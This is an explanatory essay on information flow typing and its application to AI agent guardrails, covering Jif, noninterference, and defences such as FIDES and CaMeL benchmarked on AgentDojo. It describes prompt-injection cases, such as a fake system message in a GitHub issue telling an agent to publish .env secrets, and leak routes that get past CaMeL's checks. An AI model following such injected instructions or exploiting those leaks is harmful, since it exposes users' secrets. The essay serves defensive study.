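# Why programmers rejected information flow typing, and what that predicts for AI agent guardrails

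## What information flow typing checks

Information flow typing checks, before a program runs, that it cannot pass data to places where the data should not go. The programmer labels some data "secret", for instance, and the compiler (the software that translates source code into something a machine can run) rejects any code that could let that data reach somewhere public. The guarantee is unusually strong because it holds for every possible run of the program and covers indirect leaks as well as plain copying. Researchers have had working languages built on this check, called security-typed languages, since the late 1990s, but few programmers use them. In *Implicit Flows* (2008), King, Hicks and colleagues observed that such tools "have seen little use in practice", while weaker checks had caught on. Engineers are now placing the same labels and checks around AI agents, which are language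 models that act by calling tools such as email, files or web requests. Whether the old record predicts anything about the new attempt depends on exactly what the check does, which a program of a few lines can show.

### Labels and their ordering

The program below checks a password. While chasing a bug, someone added line 1 and forgot to take it out.

```
secret string stored     // the password on file
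public string guess      // what the visitor typed
public string log        // a file that support staff can read
public bool   reply      // what the visitor sees

1   log = stored
2   reply = false
3   if guess == stored
4       reply = true
```

`secret` and `public` are labels, which mark who may read a piece of data. (Labels can also mark how far to trust the data, as discussed below.) Public data may move into a secret variable, since that only narrows the audience, but secret data may not move into a public variable. The usual symbol for "may flow to" is ⊑, so the whole policy here is public ⊑ secret, plus the rule that every label may flow to itself.

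Two labels in this order form the smallest useful lattice. A lattice is an ordering of labels that settles which flows are legal and which label results when a program combines data. With only two levels the second job is easy, because anything computed partly from a secret is secret. It gets more interesting with four. Suppose the visitor's guess is private too (people often type the password for some other site by mistake), while the stored password belongs to the site:

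```
            both
           /    \
     visitor    site
           \    /
           public
```

Data may flow upwards along the lines. Visitor data may not flow to `site`, nor site data to `visitor`. When two values are combined, the result's label is the join (⊔) of their labels, which is the least restrictive label to which both may flow. For example, `visitor ⊔ site = both`, and `public ⊔ site = site`. Only someone permitted by both the visitor and the site may read data labelled `both`.

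In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976), Denning argued that the ordering must behave this way or the policy contradicts itself. If `b = a` and `c = b` are both legal, then `c = a` must be legal, because the two assignments together already copy `a` into `c`. If `c = a + b` is legal, then `c = a` must be too, since `b` might be zero. Denning's four-level example was the military classification levels from unclassified to top secret, where the join of two labels is the higher one.

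### Explicit flows, implicit flows and the assignment rule

Line 1 is an explicit flow because it copies the secret directly into a public variable. The compiler compares the two labels and rejects the line because secret ⊑ public is false.

Line 4 is harder to catch. It copies only the constant `true`, which isn't secret, but anyone who reads `reply` afterwards knows whether the guess was right. This is an implicit flow, in which data escapes through the choice of which branch runs. The leak happens even when line 4 doesn't run, because the visitor sees `false` and learns that the guess was wrong. A monitor that inspected assignments only as they happened would have nothing to inspect in that case.

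The solution is to give the program's current position its own label, called the program-counter label, or pc, after the program counter that tracks which instruction a machine is executing. It represents what an observer could learn from knowing that execution had reached a given line. It starts out public. When the compiler enters a branch, it joins pc with the condition's label. After the branch, it restores the old value, because the next line runs either way, so reaching it reveals nothing about the condition. The condition in line 3 mixes public and secret data, so pc is secret throughout the body of the `if`.

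For any assignment `x = e`, the compiler then requires

label(e) ⊔ pc ⊑ label(x).

| Line | Label of the expression | pc | Join | Label of the target | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | secret | public | secret | public | rejected |
| 2 | public | public | public | public | accepted |
| 4 | public | secret | secret | public | rejected |

The rule has barely changed in fifty years. *Filament* (Ching, Zhou and Zhang, 2026), which presents a library that brings the check to Rust, states it as two conditions, one on the expression and one on pc. These are equivalent to a single condition on their join, because a join may flow somewhere exactly when both of its parts may.

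Why do this before the program runs? J. S. Fenton had already designed a machine in the early 1970s that kept a program-counter label during execution and blocked illegal assignments on the spot. But blocking is itself visible. Denning pointed out that a program could commit violations on purpose, as many as the secret number it wanted to send, and its owner could count them in the record of aborted operations. Letting labels rise instead of blocking anything has its own hole, which Denning illustrated with a program of Fenton's. Take a secret `a`, and let `b` and `c` start as public, with labels that go up whenever secret data arrives:

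```
b = false;  c = false
if not a:  c = true
if not c:  b = true
```

If `a` is true, the machine skips the second line, `c` stays false and public, and the third line sets `b` to true under a public condition. If `a` is false, `c` becomes true and secret, the machine skips the third line, and `b` stays false and public. Either way, `b` ends up equal to `a` but labeled public. The labels are wrong because a line that doesn't run can't raise a label. A compiler avoids this error by examining both branches.

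Information flow typing judges what code might do, so it can reject programs that leak nothing. King and colleagues give the example of a program that tests a secret and sets a public variable to 1 in either case. The typing rule rejects this program even though it is harmless. Some false alarms are unavoidable. Denning and Denning (1977) showed in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* that a procedure that always separated leaky programs from harmless ones would also solve the halting problem. It could decide for any program whether it ever stops, which no procedure can do. How often false alarms occur in real code has been measured separately.

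### What a program that passes guarantees

The property behind all this is noninterference: secret inputs make no difference to public outputs. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003), in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, put it as a statement about pairs of runs. For a program C and any two starting states s₁ and s₂,

s₁ =_L s₂ ⇒ C(s₁) ≈_L C(s₂).

The left side means the two states agree on every public value, though their secrets may differ. The right side means an observer who sees only public data cannot tell the two results apart. One run is not enough to determine whether a program has this property, which is another reason it is awkward to enforce by monitoring programs as they execute.

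The guarantee depends on what the observer can see. The usual version compares public values and leaves out running time and power consumption. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues note that current tools also ignore whether the program stops at all. They argue that in programs that produce output, this omission leaks more than the one bit often assumed in the field.

Noninterference can also protect integrity, which concerns how far data can be trusted. It then guarantees that untrusted inputs do not affect trusted outputs. This reverses the ordering used for confidentiality, so trusted data may flow into untrusted places but not the other way. Kenneth Biba noticed the symmetry in the 1970s. The password program shows why one might want both guarantees. Adding the line `stored = guess` is harmless for confidentiality, since it moves public data into a secret variable, but it violates integrity,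 since any visitor could overwrite the password. The symmetry is imperfect, as Sabelfeld and Myers point out, because a program can spoil trusted data without outside influence by computing the wrong answer. Labels cannot reveal such errors because they record only where data came from.

### A correct password check fails the test

Without line 1, the program does only what every login page does, but the compiler still rejects line 4. It does so correctly, because the public reply depends on a secret. Suppose the program runs twice with the guess "swordfish", once with "swordfish" on file and once with "marigold". Only the secret differs between the two runs, yet the public reply changes. *Relaxing Noninterference*, a Carnegie Mellon University lecture note, calls the attempt to apply noninterference to a password checker "doomed to failure" for this reason.

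If the password is one of a million equally likely strings, a single guess leaks on average about 0.00002 bits, where one bit is the answer to an evenly balanced yes-or-no question. That is too little to justify giving up logins. But the lattice doesn't distinguish small leaks from large ones, so a usable language needs a way for the programmer to make exceptions. The standard way is declassification, a deliberate release of data to a less restrictive label. Noninterference no longer holds for data released this way, and someone has to judge whether the release was wise.

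### The same check in Jif

Jif extends Java with information flow labels and is the most developed of the security-typed languages. Myers (1999), in *JFlow*, which was the language's first name, used a password file as an example. Cut down to one account and a numeric password, it looks roughly like this:

```
class PasswordFile authority(root) {
    private int{root:} stored;

    boolean check(int guess) where authority(root) {
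        boolean match = false;
        if (guess == stored) {
            match = true;
        }
        return declassify(match, {guess});
    }
}
```

A Jif label is written in braces and names people or roles, called principals, instead of levels such as "secret". It lists an owner, then a colon, then the readers whom that owner permits. The label `{root:}` means that root, the system administrator, owns the data and lets nobody else read it. The owner always counts as a reader. A label can hold several such policies, and a reader must satisfy all of them. Askarov and Sabelfeld, who wrote an online poker protocol in Jif in 2005, give the example `{Bob: Alice; Alice: Carol}`, which marks data that only Alice can read, because only she appears in both policies. Data with the empty label `{}` is public.

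The lattice carries over directly. Data may flow to a label that adds policies or removes readers, and the join of two labels contains the policies of both. In *Protecting Privacy Using the Decentralized Label Model*, Myers and Liskov give an example with two parties who distrust each other. Bob gives his tax data, labelled `{Bob: Bob}`, to a program that consults a tax firm's private database, labelled `{Preparer: Preparer}`. Everything computed from both carries both policies, so neither party can read it. Bob gets his finished tax form only because the firm's code, acting with the firm's authority, removes the firm's own policy, which it can do without being able to remove Bob's.

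Most of the labels in the password class are missing because the compiler supplies them. The parameter `guess` has none, so the method accepts a guess with any label, and `{guess}` refers to that label. Inside the `if`, pc is `{guess; root:}`, so the compiler infers that `match` must have a label at least that restrictive. The return value has the default label `{guess}`, which has no policy from root, so a plain `return match` would fail. The `declassify` expression removes root's policy, which is legal only because the `authority(root)` clauses give this code the right to act for root. By Myers's count, the full version differs from ordinary Java in three annotations: the grant of authority, the declassification and the label on the stored passwords. It must also explicitly catch two kinds of error. Myers and Liskov concede that neither can occur there, but the compiler does not try to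 prove it.

### Two weaker relatives

Taint tracking follows marked data through explicit flows only. The scripting languages Perl and Ruby have long offered a version of it, and such tools have found many real security holes. In the login program, a taint tracker would report line 1 but miss line 4. Tracking explicit flows is sometimes enough, but it can miss large leaks. King and colleagues describe a function that compares a secret number with one the caller supplies and prints "greater" or "smaller". Cqual, a C analyser that tracks explicit flows, reports nothing wrong with it. If the secret is a 32-bit number, a caller can find it in 32 calls by halving the remaining range each time.

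Access control only determines which programs may open the password file. The login program has to read the file, so it gets permission, and after that no access rule prevents line 1. Access control can't limit permission to programs that never leak what they read because, as Sabelfeld and Myers observe, it provides no way to identify them. Denning thought a practical system needed both access control and information flow checks, since a lattice of labels does not determine, for example, who may run a given piece of code.

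### From Denning to Jif

Denning's 1976 lattice gave a common form to a variety of systems that mostly checked flows at run time. A year later Denning and Denning moved the check into the compiler, but nobody built the language they proposed. In 1996 Dennis Volpano and colleagues recast the rules as a type system, the kind of check that already stops a programmer from adding a number to a word. They proved for a small language that every program that passes the check satisfies noninterference. Myers then extended the approach to most of Java, including objects and exceptions, which made the same proof much harder. In 2000 Myers and Liskov still listed it as future work. Myers took on a full language because static flow analysis had gained little acceptance by 1999 despite its long history, and Myers attributed much of that low acceptance to earlier designs that were too restrictive for writing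 real programs.

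## How the same checks are placed around an AI agent

Jif's compiler can examine both branches of an `if` because a programmer has already written them. An AI agent's language model usually picks each step after it receives the result of the last one, so there is no full sequence of actions to examine in advance. Most checks for agents therefore run alongside the agent, outside the model, and inspect tool calls instead of assignments.

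### The agent loop and prompt injection

An agent is a loop run by ordinary software. The software sends the model the conversation so far and descriptions of the available tools. The model replies with either an answer for the user or a request to call a tool, say `send_email`, with arguments that it chooses. The request is only text, and the software decides whether to carry it out. If it does, it adds the tool's result to the conversation and sends everything to the model again. The natural place for a check is between the request and its execution, and *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) puts its check there.

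On every pass through the loop, the software joins the developer's instructions, the user's request and whatever the tools have fetched into one long string, and the model has no reliable way to tell which parts to obey. Suppose a user asks the agent to summarize recent emails about a project and send the summary to the user's manager. If one of those emails contains an instruction to send the top message in the mailbox to an outside address, the agent may do that too, using tools the user gave it. In this attack, called prompt injection, text in the data an agent reads makes it follow an attacker's instructions. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that the name comes from SQL injection, an older attack in which a database executes text that a visitor typed into a form.

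Developers can tell the model to ignore instructions inside data, or train a second model to spot attacks. Both make attacks less likely to succeed. Willison objects that in security a filter that catches 99% of attacks fails, because an attacker can keep looking for the other 1%. Labels avoid this problem because they record where text came from, whatever its content. Costa and colleagues assume that the attacker controls some of the data that tools fetch and can observe the effects of some tool calls. They also assume that the user, the developer's instructions and the tool descriptions are trustworthy.

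### The context label and the rule for tool calls

Each piece of data gets a label with two parts, one for integrity and one for confidentiality. The simplest version has four labels:

```
          (untrusted, private)
           /                \
(untrusted, public)    (trusted, private)
           \                /
           (trusted, public)
```

Data may flow upwards, as in the earlier lattices. The user's request normally starts at the bottom.

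The software also keeps one running label for the conversation. This is the context label C, the combined label of everything the agent's model has read so far in a run. When a tool returns a result with label r, the software updates it:

C ← C ⊔ r.

Before it carries out a call f(a₁, …, aₙ), the software checks that

C ⊑ P_f and label(aᵢ) ⊑ P_{f,i} for every argument i.

P_f is the most restrictive context label that the tool's policy accepts, and P_{f,i} is the most restrictive label it accepts for argument i. An argument the model wrote carries the label C, because anything in the conversation might have influenced it. An argument the software inserted from storage, without showing it to the model, keeps its own label.

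This is close to the assignment rule for programs, label(e) ⊔ pc ⊑ label(x). The tool corresponds to the variable x and the argument to the expression e. The context label corresponds to pc, because it records what might have influenced the decision to make the call. But a compiler restores pc after a branch, while the context label never falls, because the model rereads the whole conversation at every step.

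Tools, or wrappers around them, attach the labels to results. The prototypes in Microsoft's *Information-flow control* put these labels in the metadata of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard that agents use to reach tools run by other parties. For example, a request to post in a team's chat channel might be labeled untrusted and public as a whole, while its message text has a separate label marking it trusted and readable by two named people.

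### An agent that sorts bug reports

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) works through an agent that triages issues on GitHub, a site where programmers share code and members of the public can report faults in it. The agent has four tools:

- `read_issue` returns text labelled untrusted, and public if the project is public.
- `read_file` returns text labelled trusted and private.
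- `post_comment` publishes a reply, and its policy accepts only a public context.
- `write_file` changes a file, and its policy accepts only a trusted context.

Suppose an attacker files an issue that looks like an ordinary build failure but ends with a paragraph made to look like a system message. In that paragraph, the attacker tells the agent to open `.env`, a file where projects commonly keep passwords and keys, and to post the contents as a reply, and the model follows the instructions.

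| Call | Check | Label of the result | Context label afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| none yet | | | (trusted, public) |
| `read_issue` | passes | (untrusted, public) | (untrusted, public) |
| `read_file(".env")` | passes | (trusted, private) | (untrusted, private) |
| `post_comment` | fails: private ⋢ public | no result | (untrusted, private) |
| `write_file` | fails: untrusted ⋢ trusted | no result | (untrusted, private) |

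The model followed the attacker's instructions throughout, but the secret didn't leak. Reading a trusted file didn't remove the "untrusted" label, because the join keeps that label from the issue and adds "private" from the file. Even right after the first call, an attempt to overwrite a file would have failed.

Under these policies, an attacker could still make the agent publish anything that isn't private, because the context is still public after `read_issue` and `post_comment` would pass. (One passage in Microsoft's post describes `post_comment` as off limits while any untrusted content is in scope, but the code beside it sets only the confidentiality limit.) The same rules apply to honest issues as to malicious ones. Microsoft gives the agent `write_file` so that it can correct obvious typos, but once it has read an issue pointing one out, it can't make the correction unless a person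 approves.

### A reply that draws on two emails

Microsoft's second example has no attacker. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. One is from Priya and previews the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who is curious about those figures but isn't supposed to see them yet. Here the confidentiality part of a label is a set of permitted readers, and the join of two sets is their intersection, as with the readers in Jif's labels. Once the agent has read the two emails, its context label is

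{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

The policy for sending a message requires every recipient to be in that set. Marco isn't, so the agent can't send the reply on its own, whether or not the draft mentions sales. If Priya had copied Marco in, the intersection would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could send the reply.

For the same reason, the agent can't write back to Priya either, even to quote Priya's own figures. It could have done so before opening Marco's email. The order in which an agent reads things determines what it can do later, and most users wouldn't think to plan that order.

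Microsoft's sample policy for posting in a chat channel is looser than the formula. It allows the message if the context is trusted or if every member of the channel may read the content. Otherwise, a person decides. The rationale for the first condition is that an outsider can't have prompted the release if no outsider's text has entered the conversation.

### Planning without reading the data

In both examples the model reads everything, and the check limits what it can do afterwards. The two-model pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023, keeps untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions. A privileged model plans and calls tools but sees only the user's request, while a quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. The software stores the quarantined model's answers under names such as `$email-summary-1`. The privileged model can have the software display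 or pass on an answer by name without seeing what it contains.

The pattern protects the plan but not the data that passes through it. Willison credits the CaMeL paper with finding this gap. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged model makes a correct plan. An attacker who can edit the notes then changes the address, so the quarantined model extracts the wrong one and the agent sends the document to the attacker.

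CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025, closes this gap by tracking each value separately. The privileged model writes its plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python, which language models already write well. For Bob's document the plan would look roughly like this:

```
notes   = read_file("meeting notes")
address = ask_reader("What is Bob's address?", notes)
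title   = ask_reader("Which document?", notes)
doc     = fetch_document(title)
send_email(to=address, attach=doc)
```

`ask_reader` stands for a query to the quarantined model. A custom interpreter runs the program line by line and tags every value with its sources and its permitted readers. It records that `address` came from `notes`, so if outsiders can edit the notes, the address is untrusted too. The policy for `send_email` can then require a recipient from a trusted source, or require the user's approval for any other. In the formula, the context label stays at the bottom because the planner has read only the user's request, so the check depends on the labels on the arguments.

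The drawback is that the planner must write the program before it sees any data. This works for Bob's document, but not for a request to carry out today's tasks from a to-do list, where the right actions depend on what is on the list.

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built, keeps the ordinary step-by-step loop and hides data returned by a tool only when the data's label would raise the context label. The software stores the hidden data in a variable and shows the model the variable's name. It does this field by field, so the model might see an email's date but only a variable name in place of its body.

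The first request is to forward the latest three emails to a colleague as a chat message. The emails are stored in a variable, and the model can send them without reading them by passing that variable as the message text. The policy accepts this because the decision to send and the choice of recipient are trusted, even though the text isn't.

If the user asks for the emails to be summarised first, the model passes the variable to a quarantined model and gets back another variable. An attacker can still spoil the summary, for instance by emailing an instruction for the quarantined model to return nothing, but can't redirect it.

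The third request is to create a calendar event if any email asks for a meeting. The planning model needs information from untrusted text to choose its next step. FIDES can ask the quarantined model a yes-or-no question, restrict its output to true or false, and show the planning model only that value. Its labels also record the value's type, so a policy can make a small, deliberate exception to the ordinary integrity rule and accept an untrusted yes-or-no answer where it would reject an untrusted sentence. An attacker might flip the answer but can hardly fit an instruction into one bit.

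*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) comes closest to the older security-typed languages. The agent writes programs in Haskell, whose types record what effects a program may have on the outside world. The software checks each program's types before running it and returns any error to the model for another try. For example, an agent that compiles a bibliography can add only entries of type `Trusted`, and only the function that queries a publications database can produce them, so a program with a made-up citation fails the type check.

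In this design, an existing Haskell library called LIO handles information flow. LIO keeps a current label that rises with everything the program reads, much like a context label, and checks it before each write. These checks happen at run time, and the types ensure that the agent's program can't bypass the library. Unlike CaMeL's planner, the agent can read some data and then write more code in response. It can also give a job to a second agent inside a sealed computation. The second agent can use any tool its own label permits, and its label rises without affecting the first agent's.

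### Results on AgentDojo

Most of these systems have published results on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates an office workspace, travel booking, a bank account and the chat service Slack. It pairs 97 user tasks with attacks planted in the data that the agent's tools return. The benchmark has separate scores for attacks that achieve their goal and user tasks that the agent completes.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES in 2025, mainly with OpenAI's GPT-4o. They found that 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent without checks. With policies on, none succeeded against FIDES or against the ordinary agent with a context label added. AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted a few successes, but Costa and colleagues examined them by hand and ruled them out, in some cases because the policy had stopped the call before it ran. The result depends partly on the labelling, because they had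 marked as untrusted every field that any AgentDojo attack uses, and someone labelling a real mailbox has no list of such fields.

With no attack under way, the checks cut the ordinary agent's task completion from 84% to 42%, averaged equally over the four settings. FIDES completed 50% with the same checks, and 61% when it used o1, an OpenAI model trained to reason at length. The gains varied by setting. On Slack tasks, the checks cut the ordinary agent's completion from 93% to 20%, while FIDES completed 48%. On travel tasks, FIDES with GPT-4o did worse than the plain context label, 41% against 73%, because the policies let many travel tools run even in an untrusted context and the model often mishandled the variables.

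In many of the remaining failures, the policies worked as designed by making the agent refuse. Several banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which is hard to distinguish from prompt injection. Costa and colleagues found that more than 40% of the banking and Slack tasks require the agent to choose its actions based on what it reads, compared with 5% of the workspace tasks.

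CaMeL's record looks less settled. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) summarised the original results as showing that CaMeL stopped nearly all attacks with comparable task performance. Other groups later also found that it stopped nearly all attacks, but they did not find comparable task performance. *SecureClaw* (2026) tested adapted versions of the released code in June and reported that none of 629 attacks succeeded and that CaMeL completed 29 of 97 tasks. *Kairos* (2026) reported in October that 0.4% of attacks succeeded and that CaMeL completed about 40% of tasks, while two undefended agents in the same study completed 83% and 87%.

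Two groups tested CaMeL with its policies on and off, which helps show where the loss comes from. Zhou and colleagues used the Slack tasks in May 2026. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, used the banking tasks and also tested their own agent on them. That agent is written in the LLMbda calculus, a small language for agents.

| System and policies | Tested by | Model | Tasks from | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed, no attack |
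|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, off | Zhou and colleagues | GPT-5.4 | Slack | | 15 of 21 |
| CaMeL, on | Zhou and colleagues | GPT-5.4 | Slack | 0 of 210 | 7 of 21 |
| Language-Based Agent Control, off | Zhou and colleagues | GPT-5.4 | Slack | | 15 of 21 |
| Language-Based Agent Control, on | Zhou and colleagues | GPT-5.4 | Slack | 0 of 210 | 8 of 21 |
| CaMeL, off | Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | banking | 1 of 240 | 32 of 48 |
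| CaMeL, on | Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | banking | 0 of 231 | 18 of 48 |
| LLMbda agent, on | Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | banking | 2 of 432 | 36 of 48 |

The 48 banking attempts are 16 tasks tried three times each, and the 210 Slack attacks are two kinds of attack on 105 pairings. In both sets of CaMeL runs, turning on the policies cut the number of completed tasks by about half. Zhou and colleagues attribute the drop to tasks that no secure policy would allow, such as forwarding the contents of an untrusted channel to whichever user they mention. The LLMbda agent avoided most of the drop because its planner can mark in advance specific pieces of untrusted data as trusted.

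CaMeL stopped nearly every attack even with its policies off, so on this benchmark most of the protection comes from separating planning from reading, and the labels add little. Garby and colleagues sorted the 144 banking pairs of task and attack and found that in 97 of them, the attack needs a tool call that would never appear in a plan for the user's task.

The attacks are also less effective against recent models. According to *AutoDojo* (2026), AgentDojo's fixed attack succeeds less than 10% of the time against DeepSeek-v4-Pro with no defence. The labels make more difference in a harder test. In a later revision of their paper, Zhou and colleagues report an adversarial evaluation with four recent models. Adding policies raised the share of injections the agents resisted from between 58% and 85%, depending on the model, to 100%, but lowered the share of tasks they completed from between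 67% and 76% to between 40% and 48%.

### Which systems cover implicit flows

FIDES deliberately covers only explicit flows. For example, if an agent visits a public web page only when a private diary shows an appointment on Friday, the page's owner can still learn of the appointment. Costa and colleagues prove explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. It guarantees that secrets do not affect the public results of any fixed sequence of actions, but secrets may still affect which sequence occurs. They judged noninterference too restrictive because, once any tool had read something private, the agent could no longer use any tool with publicly visible effects.

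LIO, the library used in Language-Based Agent Control, imposes roughly that rule. Its current label reflects everything the program has read, so after a private read, a public write fails whichever branch the program takes. Sealed computations make the rule tolerable because a program can read private data inside one and continue outside it with its old label.

CaMeL blocks some implicit flows but misses others. Its interpreter keeps a pc label, so it blocks an email sent directly inside a branch that tests a secret bank balance. But Garby and colleagues found that the interpreter raises a variable's label only on the branch that runs, which allows the leak that Fenton described in the 1970s. A program with two such branches in a row can copy the result of the balance test into a variable that stays public and then send an email that depends on that variable.

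A second leak comes from the code around the interpreter. When a policy stops a program, ordinary Python code outside the interpreter starts another attempt. Whether the policy stops an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it. Nothing tracks that bit, so a program that exploits the retries can extract the whole secret one bit at a time. An attacker who controls only an email can't readily use either leak, because CaMeL's planner writes its program before the email is read. Both leaks matter more if the planning model makes careless mistakes or is compromised.

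Garby and colleagues designed the LLMbda calculus to rule out such mistakes. It is a minimal programming language with added operations for prompting a model, branching off a separate conversation and clearing a conversation. Every value carries a label, and so does the conversation. If a program tries to add a message to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret, the interpreter stops it, because the absence of that message in another run would also reveal something about the secret.

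They proved noninterference for every program in the language, including programs that a model writes while the agent is running, and checked the proof by computer in the proof language Lean. The proof covers the interpreter that calls the model, so there is no separate implementation that could differ from the theory. Because a language model's output is random, the guarantee is that changing a secret can't change how likely each public result is, except by affecting whether the program finishes. If two runs that differ only in their secrets fail to finish with probabilities p and q, the distributions of their public results differ by at most (p + q)/2.

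The theorem still depends on correct labels and on checks at every sensitive tool, and it allows deliberate exceptions to the integrity rule. Both successful attacks on the LLMbda agent relied on such exceptions. In each, the user asked the agent to make a payment according to a text file, the attacker replaced the file's contents, and the planner had marked those contents as trusted in advance. When Garby and colleagues removed the planner's ability to do this in runs with two other models, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed 30 of 48 attempts instead of 36 with one model, and 26 instead of 31 with the other.

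## Who has used these systems

The agents in those benchmark runs were research prototypes, and so was nearly everything people built with the older languages. That casts some doubt on the word "rejected", because people can only reject what they have had a fair chance to use. Programmers may have tried a security-typed language and dropped it, known of one and never tried it, or never had one that was ready for their work. Users who abandoned a working product would probably have the same objections to a copy of it, but an unfinished product's lack of users is much weaker evidence about a finished one.

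### Programs by researchers

In 2004 Steve Zdancewic, who had helped to develop Jif, wrote that mechanisms for enforcing information flow had "not been widely (or even narrowly!) used". Askarov and Sabelfeld quoted the remark a year later to explain why they had written a poker program in Jif. They wanted to know whether security-typed languages scaled up to real systems, and thought they could only find out by writing something substantial in one. They named two available compilers, Jif and Flow Caml, which adds labels to the functional language Caml. Their program let people play poker over a network without trusting anyone to deal. As far as they knew, it was the largest program anyone had written in a security-typed language.

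Hicks, Ahmadizadeh and McDaniel (2006), in *From languages to systems*, dismissed the earlier efforts as "toy" programs and presented an email system written in Jif as the first real-world application. They needed tools, services and language extensions beyond Jif itself to state and enforce the application's policy.

The better-known programs from these years are:

| Year | Program | Written with | Research group |
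|---|---|---|---|
| 2003 | Battleship, the board game | Jif | Cornell University |
| 2005 | Online poker | Jif | Chalmers University of Technology |
| 2006 | Email system | Jif | Pennsylvania State University |
| 2007 | Log-file utility and email client | Jif | Pennsylvania State University |
| 2007 | Web email and shared calendar | Jif | Cornell University |
| 2008 | Civitas, an electronic voting system | Jif | Cornell University |
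| 2011 | λChair, for reviewing conference papers | LIO | Stanford University |
| 2012 | GitStar, a code-hosting website | Hails, a web framework based on LIO | Stanford University |
| 2014 | Battleship again | LIO | MIT Lincoln Laboratory |

LIO checks labels at run time, so the last three programs use a method closely related to information flow typing, not information flow typing itself. All nine rows come from research groups, and Cornell and Stanford were testing tools they had designed.

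In *You Sank My Battleship!* (2014), the source of the last row, Stoughton, Johnson and colleagues noted how few case studies there had been. They also repeated another of Zdancewic's complaints from 2004, that programmers had no easy way to describe the security policies they wanted, and thought it "could have been written today". That judgement is about tools for writing policies rather than the number of users.

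For their own study, they wrote Battleship three times and counted the trusted lines in each version, meaning the code an auditor has to check because the game's security depends on it. The version in which both players trust a referee had about 480. The two versions without a referee had about 610 with access control and about 850 with LIO. Protecting a player against a malicious opponent's code seemed to require one of those two methods. One board game is limited evidence, but in this direct comparison LIO's labels left more code to audit than access control did.

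Jif is still available. *The Jif Language and Compiler*, the guide that the Cornell group publishes with the source code, recommends Java 7 (released in 2011) or later. The developers ask anyone who uses Jif to let them know. They also thank outsiders for bug reports and feedback, including Askarov, Sabelfeld, Hicks and King, who are all researchers in the field. They suggest that newcomers look at the Battleship program. According to Stoughton and colleagues, the players' strategies in that version are fixed in the code, so nobody can play it. Researchers still produce new tools of this kind, such as the Rust library Filament in 2026.

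### Military and industrial use

The military did adopt information flow labels, but in operating systems. A research grant abstract on Grantome, a database of science funding, describes this use as a long-standing defence against Trojan horses (programs that appear useful but do hidden harm). These labels have the same weakness as access control, because the operating system cannot track data inside a program that may open both secret and public files.

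*From Trusted to Secure* (Hicks, Rueda and colleagues, 2007) examined how SELinux, a set of security controls available in mainstream Linux, handled such programs. SELinux simply marked them as trusted, so 30 to 40 types of application had special privileges. One was `logrotate`, which manages log files and can email them. Even a careful reader of its source code would struggle to be sure that it never emailed a log to the wrong person, and in version 2.7.1 this could happen.

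This looks like the best opportunity a security-typed language ever had, because the labels already existed and the operating system could not enforce them inside dozens of important programs. Hicks and colleagues wrote a prototype of `logrotate` in Jif and built a service that compares a Jif program's policy with the operating system's before running it. They had to connect the two themselves because security-typed languages had too few users for anyone to have done it already. They called programming in Jif "a frustrating endeavor", though workable for small utilities.

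The US military also funded research on these languages. The Office of Naval Research and the US Air Force's research laboratory helped fund Jif, and DARPA, the Pentagon's research agency, sponsored the 2014 Battleship study. The funding is evidence of interest, but an agency can fund research for years without using the results.

For industrial use of a flow check before a program runs, the nearest case is SPARK, a restricted version of the Ada language for software where failures are dangerous. Companies have used it in aircraft and air traffic control. A SPARK programmer can attach a contract to a procedure, listing the inputs on which each output depends. For the login check it would look like this:

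```
procedure Check (Guess : in Integer; Reply : out Boolean)
  with Global  => (Input => Stored),
       Depends => (Reply => (Guess, Stored));
```

If the last line left out `Stored`, the SPARK tools would report a missing dependency, even though the stored password affects the reply only through a branch, so SPARK covers implicit flows. The contract specifies that the reply depends on the password, but it has no security labels, so someone still has to decide whether that dependency is acceptable. The contracts are also optional, so we can't infer from the number of SPARK projects how many check flows this way.

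### Which history fits the languages

There is very little evidence that anyone tried a security-typed language in production and then dropped it. The case studies were experiments, and none describes an organisation that used such a language in production. The complaints in them suggest what problems a wider trial would have run into, but they come from people who mostly favoured the idea.

It is harder to tell how many programmers knew about these languages and chose not to use them. Security specialists could easily have read about them, since the survey by Sabelfeld and Myers alone cites 147 papers, by Stoughton and colleagues' count. The developers of SELinux worked with labels every day and may well have known about the languages and decided against them. But a large specialist literature doesn't show that ordinary Java programmers had heard of Jif.

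Most of the evidence suggests that these systems weren't ready. *SIF*, by Chong, Vikram and Myers, explained in 2007 that earlier versions of Jif fixed the set of principals at compile time, so a website couldn't sign up a new user and protect that user's data under the user's own label. They removed the restriction in Jif 3.0 and used that version to write the web email and calendar programs, whose users can set their own policies while the program runs. Jif had first been published, as JFlow, eight years earlier. Hicks and colleagues were still building the connection to the operating system in 2007, and Stoughton and colleagues still lacked good tools for stating a policy in 2014.

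"Rejected" is therefore too strong a word for what most programmers did with these languages, since they never faced the choice. But capable groups worked on Jif for well over a decade, and they may have failed to produce a practical language partly because the check itself is hard to work with.

### What agent products use instead

The record for agents is shorter. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) surveys 59 papers, 21 production systems and 26 security plugins, with data up to April 2026. The production systems are widely used agents for coding, operating a computer and business work, including Claude Code, Codex and Devin. Information on these systems came from official documentation, engineering blogs, system cards (developers' reports on a system's abilities and risks) and public incident reports. Two researchers independently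 classified a random fifth of the papers and systems and reconciled their categories. One of them then classified the rest, and the other spot-checked the results.

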